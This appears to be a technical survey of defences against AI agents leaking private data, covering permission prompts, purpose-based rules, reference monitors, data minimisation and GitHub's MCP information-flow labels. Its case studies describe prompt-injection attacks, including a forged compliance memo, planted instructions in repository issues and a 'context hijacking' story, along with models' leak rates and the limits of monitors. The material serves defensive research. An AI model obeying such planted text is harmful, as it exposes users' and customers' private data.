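Stanley and colleagues tried three planted attacks on 20 tasks. Against an unprotected agent, an attack that added the user's Social Security number to every tool call succeeded in 75% of tasks, and the other two succeeded wherever they applied. None succeeded against GAAP. GAAP completed 76.0% of the ordinary tasks, compared with 81.0% for the unprotected agent, and 64.6% on AgentDojo, compared with 80.1%. Remembering permissions across the 20 tasks reduced the number of questions from 85 to 55. Because GAAP can group questions, the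 user faced 39 interruptions, about two per task, instead of 58.

GAAP trusts neither the model nor its context, so unlike the Teams rule, it makes no exception for trusted context. It treats a mistaken disclosure the same as one caused by an attacker. It doesn't protect private data that the user types into the request, or prevent an injection from changing the agent's actions in ways that disclose no private data.

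Whether GAAP would have stopped PixelLeak probably depends on how the annotations define the recipient. If the recipient is the new public repository, GAAP would have no stored answer and would ask the developer for permission. If the recipient is GitHub as a whole, the developer may have already permitted sharing the project with it, in which case GAAP would allow the upload. Permissions for public platforms have to specify the audience, not just the company that runs the service.

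### Asking at the time or deciding in advance

GAAP's stored answers suggest that users could settle most releases beforehand. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) tested this with 113 people who had no professional software background. They supervised a simulated day of 18 agent actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for. There was no attacker, so these seven actions resembled PixelLeak more than Invariant's leak. One group approved each action as it came up. Another first set a standing rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories, including sending or publishing information. A third relied on a model to review the actions.

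The standing rules reduced the average number of prompts from 18.0 to 10.9, but they blocked 20.1 percentage points less of the overreach than approving each action did. Participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which left those decisions for later. A person had approved 133 of the 148 overreaching actions that went ahead, so careless "allow" rules were not the main reason. Yan compared whole designs, so it isn't clear why this group approved more. Perhaps people who have written rules assume that whatever reaches them has already passed some check.

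Advance permission works best when the item and the audience are enough to decide whether a release is acceptable, regardless of what the agent writes. A traveler who lets an airline have their date of birth is unlikely to want to reconsider at the next check-in. Advance refusals can be even more useful. A company could decide once that no image of an internal product may go to a public repository, and the rule would apply even when its developers were tired. A refusal would also keep developers from making decisions about data they may have no right to release, such as a utility company's billing records.

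The release notes are different because the item and the audience stay the same every month and only the text changes. Once the user gives GAAP standing permission to share the commit history with the public repository, GAAP will let through both the good note and the bad one. Somebody has to read the text before each release, preferably next to the private entries behind it, with a reminder that the text will be public. This requires one prompt per release, which is a small burden.

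A support agent that answers hundreds of strangers a day can't ask for approval of every reply. Its operator could instead decide what may be released before the agent reads anything. A person would select and check the private documents that strangers may learn from, and the agent would have access to no others. The agent would have less information to use, but a person would have read everything it could disclose.

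## When the permission depends on the purpose

Suppose an online shop uses an agent to arrange deliveries. The agent sends each customer's postal address to a courier, which needs it to deliver the parcel. The courier also has an advertising business that posts leaflets, which the shop's customers never agreed to receive. The courier may therefore use the address for delivery but not for marketing.

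A reader set can't express a permission that depends on purpose. If the courier is in the set, permitted flow lets the agent send it the address for either delivery or advertising, and if the courier isn't, the agent can't send the address even for delivery. The shop could list the courier's delivery and advertising businesses as separate readers, which works if each has its own account. If they share an account, both names refer to the same reader, and the two purposes differ only in what the courier does with the address afterwards.

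*Purpose Based Access Control for Privacy Protection* (Bertino, Li and Byun) observes that privacy policies are about which data someone uses for which purposes, rather than which user performs which action on which object. Laws often focus on purpose too. *On the Semantics of Purpose Requirements in Privacy Policies* (Tschantz, Datta and Wing, 2011) quotes a European Union rule that organizations must collect personal data for "specified, explicit and legitimate purposes" and not process it further in ways incompatible with those purposes. This principle is called purpose limitation.

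### Contextual integrity

Contextual integrity, developed by the information scientist Helen Nissenbaum, is the best-known theory of why the same disclosure can be fine in one setting and wrong in another. *Contextual Integrity Up and Down the Data Food Chain* (Nissenbaum, 2019) defines privacy as the appropriate flow of personal information. On this view, sharing is not in itself a loss of privacy. Health care, education and friendship each have their own norms about who tells whom what, and a flow violates privacy when it breaks the norms of its context.

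A complete norm has five parameters. The least familiar is the transmission principle, the condition under which the information may pass, such as consent, confidentiality or a judge's warrant. The table applies the parameters to a US health privacy rule that Nissenbaum cites and to the courier, and compares them with a reader set.

| Parameter | Psychotherapy notes | Delivery | In a reader set? |
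|---|---|---|---|
| Sender | a health care organization | the shop | No |
| Recipient | the patient | the courier | Yes |
| Subject | the patient | the customer | No |
| Information type | psychotherapy notes | a postal address | No, though each piece of data has its own set |
| Transmission principle | only with the psychiatrist's prior approval | with the customer's consent | No |

Purpose is not one of the five parameters in Nissenbaum's theory. Purposes help define the context, and people and organizations are identified by the roles they play in it. The courier acting as a carrier is therefore a different recipient from the courier acting as an advertiser, even if the agent reaches both through one account. The computer scientist Anupam Datta has urged Nissenbaum to add a sixth parameter for use, and by 2019 she was "increasingly persuaded". One reason is that a company can obtain data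 by taking over the firm that holds it, even if the norms would forbid that firm to share the data with the company.

Nissenbaum also rejects the division of data into public and private. Fellow shoppers can see what is in someone's cart, but that doesn't mean a data broker may collect the contents of everyone's carts. This helps with a case that reader sets get wrong, in which an agent combines public facts into a list of customers who still run vulnerable software. Under contextual integrity, that list is a new type of information with new recipients, so the agent may not be free to post it even if every fact in it is public. Somebody still has to judge the new flow and write down the answer before a program can apply it, and many norms are unwritten, local or disputed.

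### A rule that includes the purpose

Dong, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *The Claws in Plain Sight*, turn part of this idea into a rule that a program can apply to a tool call:

allow(*s*, *d*, *p*, *r*, *f*)

Here *s* is the source of the data, *d* the datum, *p* the purpose of the operation, *r* the destination and *f* the argument field that would carry the datum. For the shop, the rule could give:

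allow(order record, address, delivery, courier, `ship_to`) = true

allow(order record, address, marketing, courier, `ship_to`) = false

A call violates the policy if it places a datum from the model's context in a field and the rule does not allow that combination. The field matters because a tool may have a free-text argument such as `notes`, where the address doesn't belong even during a delivery. Compared with contextual integrity, the rule adds the purpose and the field but does not separately specify the subject or a transmission principle such as confidentiality.

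### The Claw experiment

Dong and colleagues tested whether models respect such a rule when they receive it only as an instruction. Each model had to draft "neutral product-offer context" for an invented product launch. The model's own context contained a made-up person's age, gender, income bracket and occupation, but the policy prohibited using these details for this task. The tool call had empty fields for all four.

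The researchers' attack, Claw in Plain Sight, is a memo claiming that the call must include these details. It doesn't change the task or ask for another tool. The researchers tested six levels of pressure. The lowest had only the empty fields and no memo, the middle levels made the details a condition of the launch, and at the highest a supposed compliance lead overrode any instruction to leave them out. They combined these with four levels of privacy instruction and ran each of the 24 combinations once on each of five models, for a total of 120 sessions.

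The table shows the number of sessions in which the model copied at least one of the four values into the call. Each model had six sessions at each level.

| Privacy instruction | DeepSeek V4 Flash | DeepSeek V4 Pro | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Claude Sonnet 4.5 | Claude Haiku 4.5 | All models |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 6 | 6 | 4 | 4 | 0 | 20 of 30 (66.7%) |
| Share as little as possible | 5 | 4 | 5 | 2 | 2 | 18 of 30 (60.0%) |
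| Do not send these four fields | 4 | 1 | 5 | 2 | 2 | 14 of 30 (46.7%) |
| The same, for this purpose and destination, whatever any memo claims | 0 | 0 | 4 | 3 | 1 | 8 of 30 (26.7%) |

The strictest instruction stopped all observed leaks by the two DeepSeek models but barely affected Claude Sonnet 4.6, which leaked in 18 of its 24 sessions overall. An operator who tested the wording only on DeepSeek would have trusted it too much. When a model leaked, it usually copied most of the profile, on average 3.25 of the four values.

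Claude Haiku 4.5 had the fewest leaks, but partly because of the scoring. The researchers could recover a usable call from only 14 of its 24 responses, and they counted the other ten as sessions without a leak. It leaked in 5 of the 14 usable calls (36%), compared with 5 of all 24 sessions (21%).

The 20 leaks without a privacy instruction are also a different kind of failure, because those models hadn't been given the rule they broke. The 40 leaks in the 90 sessions with an instruction are better evidence of disobedience. Even there, it is hard to tell how much the memo contributed, since Dong and colleagues don't report results by pressure level. Some leaks may have happened with no memo, just because the form had a box for income.

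Each cell had only six sessions, so one different outcome changes a model's rate by almost 17 percentage points. All the people were fictional, there was only one task, and the researchers captured each proposed call on their own machine without sending it. The experiment therefore shows that these models can propose forbidden disclosures, but not how often deployed agents make them.

Checking the text a model writes around a tool call would have been a poor safeguard, because the DeepSeek models accounted for 26 of the 60 leaks and none of their responses contained the wording about exceptions that the researchers searched for.

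### The reference monitor

Dong and colleagues also built a policy engine, which they call a reference monitor. It takes no policy information from the model:

1. The tool's registration fixes the destination and the fields that may carry data.
2. The active task supplies the purpose.
3. Each protected item carries its source and the uses its policy allows.
4. The monitor searches every field of the call for protected values and applies the rule to each one it finds.
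5. It can block the call, ask for confirmation, replace or remove a value, or let the call through. If several of these apply, the strictest wins.

A person's confirmation covers only the exact call they approved, so the agent can't change an argument afterwards. The monitor also detects some values computed from protected data. Suppose a registered function turns an income of $175,000 into the customer tier "premium", and the policy allows the tier to be used for financing but not for marketing. The monitor then blocks a marketing call containing "premium", even though the call doesn't include the income itself.

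In a check with 12 of the synthetic sessions, the monitor blocked all 12 calls that copied the profile. In another check, it blocked nine prohibited calls and let three authorized ones run. Both checks replayed prepared calls to a harmless local destination, with complete and correct labels. They confirm that the blocking code works, but they did not test how the monitor would perform with a live agent.

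The monitor finds only exact values and the results of registered functions, so it would miss a paraphrase in the release notes. A scanner with a list of customers' names would miss it too.

### When no single call is wrong

Private data can also affect a call without appearing in it. Pandey, Jain and colleagues (2026), in *Local Allow, Global Deny*, give the example of a scheduling assistant that may tell others when its user is free, but may not let the reasons for busy times affect what it offers. The assistant offers 10 o'clock when a busy slot is an ordinary meeting, and 11 o'clock when the same slot is a confidential interview. Neither offer looks wrong, because both times are free in both cases, but the assistant has broken the rule by letting the hidden reason change its offer.

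Their requirement is a looser form of noninterference, defined over any two runs, *t* and *t*′:

if low(*t*) = low(*t*′) and D(hi(*t*)) = D(hi(*t*′)), then α(obs(*t*)) = α(obs(*t*′))

Here low is the task and other unrestricted input, hi is the sensitive context, and D selects the part of that context that the purpose allows the agent to use (the free and busy times). The agent's disclosure is obs, and α keeps only the features relevant to the policy, such as which slots the agent offers. If everything the agent may use is the same in two runs, those features of its disclosure must also be the same.

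Any single run satisfies this condition, because a run always matches itself. A monitor that looks at one run at a time and never raises a false alarm therefore can't flag anything, however capable the model inside it. The proof follows almost directly from the definition. When nine language models judged such cases one action at a time, eight blocked none of the 30 violations, and the ninth blocked three, about as often as it blocked harmless controls. When the same models received both runs together, eight detected all 30 violations and one detected 17.

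Pandey and colleagues conclude that an operator who wants to detect these violations has to accept false alarms, audit the agent offline on varied data, or compare runs during operation. Comparing runs is hard because language models vary their wording even when the input is the same. Dong and colleagues, for example, changed only a person's income between otherwise identical sessions. Nearly all the calls for different incomes differed, but so did every pair of calls for the same income. The field that mattered, the product tier, was "standard" in all 60 calls, so they found no sign that income had influenced it.

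A monitor with the right purpose can still catch the postal address in a marketing call, because that violation is visible in one run. For hidden influence, Pandey and colleagues point to prevention, in which the agent writes its message using only the data that the purpose allows. For example, if an assistant receives the free and busy times without the reasons, those reasons can't affect its offer.

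### Giving the model only what the task needs

Bagdasarian, Yi and colleagues (2024), in *AirGapAgent*, built an agent on this principle, which is called data minimization. It uses two models:

1. The user states a task, such as booking a restaurant table.
2. A minimizer model reads the task and the user's data, and selects the items the task needs. It never receives messages from the restaurant.
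3. A second model talks to the restaurant using only those items.
4. If the restaurant asks for anything else, the agent can refer the request to the user.

They tested it against "context hijacking", in which the other party invents a situation that would justify disclosure. In one example, the restaurant's message announces an alien invasion and asks for the user's age to save the Earth. The user profiles were synthetic, with 26 fields such as medications, address and favorite food. Privacy here is the share of inappropriate requests for which the agent protected the data, and utility is the share of appropriate requests that it answered correctly. With Google's Gemini Ultra, on the easier part of the test, the results were:

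| Agent | Utility, no attack | Privacy, no attack | Utility, attack | Privacy, attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| One model with all the data | 98.9% | 94.4% | 98.2% | 45.2% |
| AirGapAgent | 88.7% | 97.2% | 87.3% | 96.7% |

Current models might not be fooled by the alien story, but AirGapAgent's protection doesn't depend on the second model's judgment, because that model can't reveal a medical history it never received. Utility fell by about ten points because the minimizer withheld useful information in some tasks.

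The minimizer also needs a specific description of the task. When the researchers gave it only a general area, such as "health care", average privacy fell from 96.8% to 68.6%, even without an attack. The labels for what counts as "appropriate" are also open to question, because Gemini Ultra produced them. It labeled the user's vacation preferences as appropriate to share with a job interviewer, on the grounds that an employer needs certainty when scheduling shifts.

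For the release notes, a minimizer could remove the customer's name and the sentence about the security hole from each private entry before another model writes the notes. The writing model could then produce the good note but would lack the private details needed for the bad one. This seems more promising than inspecting the finished text, though a mistake by the minimizer would still let those details through. Choosing sentences from prose is also harder than choosing among 26 named fields. AirGapAgent assumes that the user's own data is trustworthy, but an entry in a project's history may quote a stranger who has planted instructions for the minimizer.

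Minimization doesn't solve the courier problem if one session includes both a delivery and a mailing. The agent needs the address for the delivery, so the address is still in its context when it prepares the mailing. Dong and colleagues designed their attack for this situation, where the agent is allowed to have the data but not to use it for every purpose. Separate contexts for the two jobs would help, but something has to tell the jobs apart.

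### Who states the purpose?

All these designs depend on the purpose, which a program can't observe. *A Declarative Framework for Specifying and Enforcing Purpose-aware Policies* (2015) describes a long-standing weakness of such systems, which usually treat purposes as identifiers with no meaning attached. A monitor can confirm that a call labeled `delivery` matches a permission labeled `delivery`, but it can't confirm that a delivery will take place. The user, the operator or a model has to supply the label.

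In *Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents*, Zhu and Wang (2026) describe a system that derives a short-lived certificate from the user's request. If the user asks for a summary of recent records, the certificate covers reading and summarizing, and the agent cannot use the export tool for that request, even if its credentials allow it. The certificate can only narrow what the agent may do, so a mistaken one may allow more than the user requested but never more than the operator's policy permits. In 306 trials with real models, no unsafe action ran to completion, but the system accepted unsafe authority at rates of 9% to 27%, always as drafts awaiting a further step. Removing those drafts made the agent considerably less useful.

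A request may also leave out the purpose. "Send this customer's address to the courier" could be for a delivery or a mailing. An outsider can't easily change what the user typed, but the user can lie about the purpose. This matters little when the data is the user's own, but an employee who wants a mailing list has a reason to claim the addresses are for deliveries.

An operator can fix the purpose when setting up the agent, for example by giving the delivery agent access to addresses and the marketing agent none. Neither a stranger's memo nor an employee's false claim can then change it. But each purpose needs its own agent or workflow, and someone has to add any unforeseen purpose before an agent can serve it. According to Tschantz and colleagues, older systems that attached purposes to job roles had a related problem, since a person in the right role could still use the data for something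 else. The operator may also prefer a broad definition of the purpose. Tschantz and colleagues quote a bank's policy that employees may access customer information "for business purposes only", which seems to include marketing.

A model can infer a purpose for tasks that nobody planned for, without any work from the user or operator. The accuracy of its guess depends on the text it reads, so whoever wrote that text can influence the guess. In the Claw experiment, the memo's author tried to make personal details look necessary for the task. AirGapAgent keeps outsiders' messages away from the model that guesses, but this also excludes anything they might legitimately add.

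An auditor with the full record can't always determine the purpose afterwards either. Tschantz and colleagues describe a physician who sends a patient's X-ray to a private practice that the physician also owns, which might be for diagnosis, for profit or for both. In their account, an action is for a purpose if the person chose it while planning to achieve that purpose. An auditor can work out the best plans for treating the patient and rule out treatment as the reason if none of them includes sending the X-ray. If one does, the auditor still can't confirm that treatment was the reason. Similarly, the shop's auditor can tell that an address sent to the courier with no parcel to deliver was not for delivery, but one sent with a real order could have been for delivery and another purpose too.

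These choices also don't control what the courier does with the address. Once the courier has it for a delivery, they can print it on a leaflet too, and only a contract or the law restricts that use.

Tschantz and colleagues suggest that purpose may work better as a guide for writing rules than as something the rules check. They expect that many hospitals would forbid physicians to refer patients to their own practices, or require a second opinion. The shop could likewise let an address leave only in the `ship_to` field of a call that creates a shipment for a paid order. A program can check every part of that rule without knowing why anyone made the call. The rule would wrongly block a free replacement for a broken item until someone added an exception.

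## Who assigns the labels and who enforces them

A label on private data protects it only if the label is correct and a program outside the model enforces it. In 2026, GitHub and Microsoft built an experimental system for both labeling and enforcement. GitHub's MCP server labels what an agent reads, and GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent for the command line, tracks the labels and checks them before making a tool call.

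### One label from server to decision

Suppose the agent in the running example has read a stranger's issue and now opens a file in the private repository. In Microsoft's description of the prototype, the file's label takes this route:

1. GitHub's server checks the repository's visibility and labels the file "private" and "trusted".
2. The server sends the label along with the text, in an MCP field for extra data called `_meta`. Clients that don't recognize the label can ignore it.
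3. Copilot CLI combines the file's label with its context label. The context already contains the stranger's issue, so it is now private and untrusted.
4. The model proposes a call to `add_issue_comment`, and Copilot CLI attaches the context label to it.
5. A policy engine compares the labeled call with the policy for that tool. A public post from a private and untrusted context fails, so the comment can't go out automatically.

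Copilot CLI computes the label, so the model can't lower it. A label can cover just part of a call. In Microsoft's example, only two named people may read the text of a chat message, while the rest of the call is public.

Users have to turn on labeling and enforcement separately. The server sends labels if its configuration includes the header `X-MCP-Features: ifc_labels`, and Copilot CLI acts on them if the user starts it with `FIDES_IFC=true`. A user who sets only the header gets labels that nothing checks. *ifc*, the documentation of the server's labeling code, notes that the enforcement engine "lives in a separate service". Microsoft calls the support in Copilot CLI experimental. Copilot CLI has policies for selected tools on GitHub's server but none for other MCP servers.

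GitHub expanded its labeling quickly. It merged the label for `get_file_contents` on May 12, 2026 (gokhanarkan, 2026, *Add ifc label for get_file_contents tool*). Version 1.3.0 added thirteen more labeling rules, including rules for commits, releases and security alerts. It was released before version 1.4.0, which GitHub published on June 17.

Copilot CLI has since gained a simpler control. According to GitHub's *Content exclusions generally available in Copilot app and CLI* (2026), administrators on business plans have been able to keep chosen files out of its context since September. As with blocking the private read, the drawback is that the agent can't use an excluded file at all.

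### How GitHub chooses a label

GitHub's server works out each label from the kind of result and the visibility of the repository:

| Result | Integrity | Confidentiality |
|---|---|---|
| File or commit in a public repository | untrusted | public |
| File or commit in a private repository | trusted | private |
| Issue | untrusted | same as the repository |
| Release | trusted | private if the repository is private or the result includes a draft |
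| Security alert | untrusted | private |
| List of collaborators | trusted | private |

The server treats files in a public repository as untrusted because an outsider can get text into them through a pull request. Only collaborators can change a private repository, so the server trusts the files in it.

Microsoft's summary describes issues in private repositories as trusted too, but GitHub's code labels all issues untrusted. Microsoft's policy lets the agent publish release notes written from private commits alone, because the context stays trusted. If the agent also opens the private issues that the commits mention, GitHub's label makes the context untrusted, and the policy blocks both the good note and the bad one.

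### The hints MCP already has

Since March 2025, an MCP server has been able to attach hints, called annotations, to each tool it offers. One is a display name. Model Context Protocol describes the other four, with cautious defaults for servers that leave them out:

| Hint | Meaning when true | Default |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | the tool changes nothing | false |
| `destructiveHint` | the tool may delete or overwrite things | true |
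| `idempotentHint` | repeating a call has no further effect | false |
| `openWorldHint` | the tool deals with outside systems | true |

None of the MCP tool annotations marks private data. Dumbris (2026) points out in *MCP Tool Annotations* that `openWorldHint` also combines the risk of taking in untrusted text with the risk of sending data out. Dumbris reports that Copilot in VS Code skips the confirmation prompt for read-only tools. This makes sense for preventing damage to files, but the call that read private data in Invariant's attack was also read-only.

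Many servers don't provide the hints. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) found annotations on 325 of 1,856 tools, or about 18%. Where hints exist, they may not reflect a deliberate choice. *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (2026) found that 52.8% of 98,291 tool definitions paired `destructiveHint` with a true `readOnlyHint`, although `destructiveHint` has no meaning for a tool that changes nothing. Excluding one large publisher, the share was 26.0%.

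A developer can't just invent a new annotation for private data. According to Block's *Scripted Tools* (2026), MCP's Kotlin SDK silently drops unknown annotations, and its TypeScript SDK rejects them. The `_meta` field accepts new entries, so it suits a prototype, but ordinary clients won't act on entries they don't recognize. Labels will work between any server and any client only if the standard defines them.

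### SEP-1913

Sam Morrow of GitHub and Robert Reichel of OpenAI have proposed such a definition in SEP-1913, "Trust and Sensitivity Annotations" (a SEP is a formal proposal to change MCP). It marks the data in requests and results, whereas the existing hints describe only tools. The markings include a sensitivity level (low, medium or high), a `privateHint`, a warning of malicious activity, and an attribution recording where the data came from.

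Dumbris summarizes how the markings spread through a session. If *s* is the session's sensitivity, *b* any of its true-or-false markings and *A* its set of attributions, then each new result *r* changes them to

*s* := max(*s*, *sᵣ*), *b* := *b* or *bᵣ*, *A* := *A* ∪ *Aᵣ*

This is a context label in another form. After the agent reads the private file, `privateHint` stays true for the rest of the session, and a client can refuse to send anything to an open-world tool. That would stop Invariant's leak, but also the release notes and the harmless typo correction, because no rule in Dumbris's summary lowers a marking.

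A client with this policy also needs to know whether a particular comment will be public, but `add_issue_comment` has the same hints for every repository. *SEP-1862* (SamMorrowDrums, 2025), another proposal from Morrow, would let a client send a call's arguments to the server before making the call and receive hints specific to it. The server could then describe a comment in a private repository as closed-world. Morrow found the same limit with access tokens. GitHub's server can't request the `repo` scope only when a user wants private data, because the scope applies to the whole tool.

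Neither proposal has become part of the standard. Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter* listed both as drafts in April 2026, and neither appears in the protocol's index of accepted and final proposals, which has entries up to October. The group discussing them can only make recommendations, and one of its open questions is whether results should carry annotations at all. An unmerged Python kit, kapil8811's *added initial scaffolding files with python ref SDK*, shows how the markings might work in practice. It includes a policy engine and an example server for a clinic.

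### Can a client believe a hint?

A server can falsely label a tool read-only when the tool deletes the user's files. When MCP's developers reviewed the original hints, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, asked how a client could use a flag "knowing that it's not trustable". Basil Hosmer, who had written the proposal, thought clients should ignore every annotation from an untrusted server, even the display name. The standard now requires clients to treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server, but it lets each client decide which servers to trust.

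Hints can be useful because companies already know many of the servers they use. A company that runs its own MCP servers, for example, has good reason to believe their annotations. Model Context Protocol suggests using annotations as one input to a policy engine that also checks other evidence. *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (2026) goes further and proposes that servers supply confidentiality labels. Companies would trust the labels from their own tools and require approved vendors or certification for others.

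Model Context Protocol distinguishes hints, which are useful even if some servers get them wrong, from contracts, which are useful only if they are true. A client can use a hint to choose which confirmation prompts to show, but the protocol would leave contracts to the authorization layer, the connection or the software that runs the tools. *MCP annotations are a UX layer, not a security layer*, by a developer writing as gyorgy, applies this objection to SEP-1913, since a server built to misdescribe its tools can mislabel its data just as easily.

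By this standard, a label used to decide which flows are permitted is a contract, because a false one lets private data out. But the harm a server can do depends on which label is false. If a server wrongly marks the data it stores as public, this adds little risk, since the server could have leaked that data directly. If it marks its own text as trusted, instructions planted in that text can get past a rule like Microsoft's and cause the agent to release data from other servers. If it describes a public destination as private, the agent may send other servers' data there.

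A client can therefore accept a stricter label from anyone, at the risk of some needless blocks, but it can accept a more lenient one only from a server whose operator is well placed to know the correct label and has no reason to lie. GitHub meets this standard for the visibility of its own repositories, but it is less able to vouch for the text inside them.

### Enforcement in the server or the client

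GitHub's server is the obvious place to block a comment that would leak private data, because it can check who is able to read the issue. It can't check what else the agent has read, but in Microsoft's design the client sends the context label with each call. A server could compare that label with the issue's audience and reject the comment if those readers shouldn't see the data. This would still depend on every client sending an accurate label, and it couldn't protect GitHub data that the agent sends to another service.

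The client can monitor calls to every server and to tools on the user's computer, so it can keep the most complete context label. However, every client has to implement the checks. Microsoft has added them to a second client, its Agent Framework for Python, where developers can turn them on in the configuration. The framework stores untrusted results in variables, as FIDES does, and either blocks a forbidden call or prompts the user.

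A client can't control what a malicious tool does with data it has already received. In *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (2026), protected data got out in 114 of 153 runs with a defense based on signed tools, and in 108 with one that also tracked information flow. The difference was six runs in which the agent itself forwarded the data. In the other 108, the tool leaked it.

Whether a label survives also depends on where it is checked. In HCP, a system described in *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* (2026), one tool can pass data to another through a special channel that checks labels. By default, however, an agent that has read the data can put it in an ordinary argument, which carries no label. A stricter setting gives the agent only a reference to the data, much like a variable in FIDES, so the agent can't copy the data into an argument unless it gets the data some other way.

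### SAMOS and Microsoft's gateway

A gateway sits between the client and the MCP servers, so an operator can add checks without changing either. *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026), a master's thesis at Brown University, describes a gateway called SAMOS. A developer or administrator gives each tool two confidentiality labels, one for what it reads and one for what it writes, and each label is either "high" or "low". Other annotations can limit the files, programs and network addresses a tool may use. SAMOS keeps a confidentiality level for each session.

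Ntousakis works through Invariant's attack. The agent lists the public issues, which sets the session to low. The planted instruction then directs the agent to a private repository, and SAMOS blocks the read because that repository is high. This is stricter than permitted flow, which blocks only the public write. The SAMOS rule would also stop an agent that reads a public bug report and then looks for the cause in private code, even if it reported its findings only to the owner. The thesis reports that SAMOS preserves the server's normal functions, but it tests SAMOS only in this case study and gives no figures for completed tasks.

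In the case study, `get_file_contents` reads both public and private repositories, so neither "high" nor "low" is always the right label for the whole tool. Ntousakis suggests either having the tool return the repository's confidentiality with each result, as GitHub's server now can, or splitting it into `get_public_file` and `get_private_file`. Splitting allows fixed labels, but the model then has to choose the right tool, and `get_public_file` has to reject requests for private repositories.

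SAMOS was also designed for a version of MCP that had sessions, and the protocol dropped them on July 28 (GitHub, 2026). Servers can now issue a "state handle", which the model passes back in later calls (Alexander, 2026, *Sessionless MCP via Explicit State Handles*). Handles suit something like a shopping basket, but they would be a poor way to look up a context label, because a model that lost the handle, or followed a planted instruction to request a new one, would start again with a clean label. The client application should supply the identifier instead.

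Microsoft has published an open-source gateway for servers that don't provide labels. To add a server, someone has to define the structure of each tool's results, write a Python function that labels them, and write or choose a policy. The servers in the 98,291-tool census had a median of 11 tools, so a typical one would need about 11 labeling functions. Microsoft has done this for selected tools in its own email and chat servers.

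### Working out labels automatically

Microsoft also suggests deriving policies from the hints servers already provide. For example, a client could:

- allow read-only tools that stay within a closed system
- allow read-only tools that reach outside systems if all the arguments are public
- ask the user before any destructive call

It could label results from outside systems "untrusted" and results from tools that require a login "private". On GitHub's server, this would label even a public repository's README "private", because `get_file_contents` requires a token with the `repo` scope. None of the three sample policies covers `add_issue_comment`. Adding a comment is neither read-only nor destructive, yet in GitLost the agent published the private README in a comment.

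A program can also assign labels based on the tool's description, as *AgentArmor* (2025) does. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (2026) compared the labels that OpenAI's o1 and human annotators gave to 80 tools. Their agreement was 0.95 on Cohen's kappa, where 0 is the agreement expected by chance and 1 is perfect agreement. In one disagreement, the humans rated the sensitivity of a tool that opens web pages as moderate because it could help with phishing, while the model rated it low.

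The people and the model read the same descriptions, so this result doesn't show that the labels match what the tools do. *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (2026) treats mismatches between description and code as a security problem and advises clients to check for them before offering a tool to the model. Dumbris proposes a proxy that infers the hints from each tool's observed behavior. That would catch a tool labeled read-only that writes a file, but a tool that had opened only public repositories would look harmless until it opened a private one.

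An operator who doesn't trust any of these guesses can leave a tool unlabeled if the policy engine handles missing labels safely. *APPA* allows partial labels and guarantees that any call it permits would also be permitted with the full set of labels. A missing label can still block useful work.

### A public repository with private parts

Even a public repository contains things that only some people can see. GitHub's rules handle several of these well, since security alerts and lists of collaborators are private whatever the repository's setting. SAMOS could get the same result for alerts by marking the tools that read them as "high".

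Results that mix public and private items are harder to handle because GitHub's server labels the whole result private. Suppose the user has saved the next release notes as a draft in the public repository, and a stranger asks what changed in the last version. When the agent lists the releases, the list includes the draft and is therefore labeled private. Under permitted flow, the agent then can't answer with the published notes, which anyone can already read. In a search across several repositories, one private match also makes every result private.

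The documentation in *ifc* defends this choice. Once all the items are in the same context, the model can copy any of them anywhere, so a separate label for each would give false assurance. SEP-1913 includes labels for individual items, but they would help only if the client also kept the items apart, for instance in separate variables.

Labeling each call separately improves on using one label per tool. In a small test with a tool that returned data of mixed sensitivity, *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* found that a worst-case label for the whole tool blocked all three attempts to post publicly, while per-call labels blocked only one.

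GitHub's rule for empty search results is too permissive. The server labels them public on the grounds that they contain no repository data. But if an agent searches a private repository for "Northfield Hospital" and finds nothing, the absence of a match is also private, and the agent could reveal it to someone without access to the repository.

### Strangers' text in a private repository

Suppose a colleague copies a customer's bug report containing a planted instruction into a file in the private repository. GitHub's server labels the file trusted because a collaborator added it. The label correctly reflects who changed the repository, but not who wrote the text. An agent that reads only this file has a trusted context, so Microsoft's policy would let it follow the instruction and publish private data.

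The permitted-flow policy would still block the public post, because the file is private regardless of who wrote it. SAMOS doesn't track trust, so it would have to rely on a rule against writing high-confidentiality data to low-confidentiality destinations.

If the colleague had pasted the report into an issue instead, GitHub would have labeled it untrusted and Microsoft's policy would have stopped the post. GitHub could treat private files as untrusted too, but then Microsoft's policy would stop nearly every public post based on private code. A narrower remedy would let maintainers mark particular folders, such as one for customer reports, as untrusted.

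### A shell command that reaches the network

Coding agents often work on a copy of the repository on the developer's computer. If the agent reads a private file there, the text doesn't pass through GitHub's MCP server, so it arrives without a label. The agent can also publish the text with `git push` or another command, using the developer's saved login. Judging by Microsoft's list of gaps, the Copilot CLI prototype would probably check neither step. Neither step would pass through a gateway for MCP calls either, unless the shell was an MCP tool.

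The sample rule for destructive tools would make the client ask about every shell command, and such repetition leads people to approve without reading. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) records which files and destinations have received sensitive data, but treats commands that start other programs cautiously because it can't follow data inside them. Flowsh's sandbox monitors what each command opens and is better suited to this case.

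The Model Context Protocol recommends network controls or a sandbox to guarantee that data can't leave. These don't distinguish between public and private repositories at the same address. VS Code's security advice therefore includes checking which Git and GitHub logins a sandboxed program can use.

### A destination the agent makes public

When an agent creates a gist, a policy engine can check the `public` argument to determine whether the agent is about to publish. If the argument is false, GitHub creates a "secret" gist, which anyone with the link can read. GitHub's server labels the content of secret gists private. That label is reasonably cautious when an agent reads a secret gist, but misleading when an agent writes one, because access isn't limited to a fixed group of people. Treating every new gist as public would be safer.

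Repositories raise a problem of timing. GitHub's labels contain only the word "private", and the client asks GitHub for the actual readers when the agent is about to write. This keeps the list current, so a colleague who has lost access no longer counts as a reader. But if the agent reads a private file and then makes that repository public, GitHub's answer changes to "everyone", and the agent can post the file anywhere. Besides treating the change itself as a release, the policy engine could record the readers when the agent opens the file and require

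A(*s*) ⊆ R(*d* when read) ∩ R(*d* now)

Changing the repository's setting would then not let the agent send the file to anyone who couldn't read it before.
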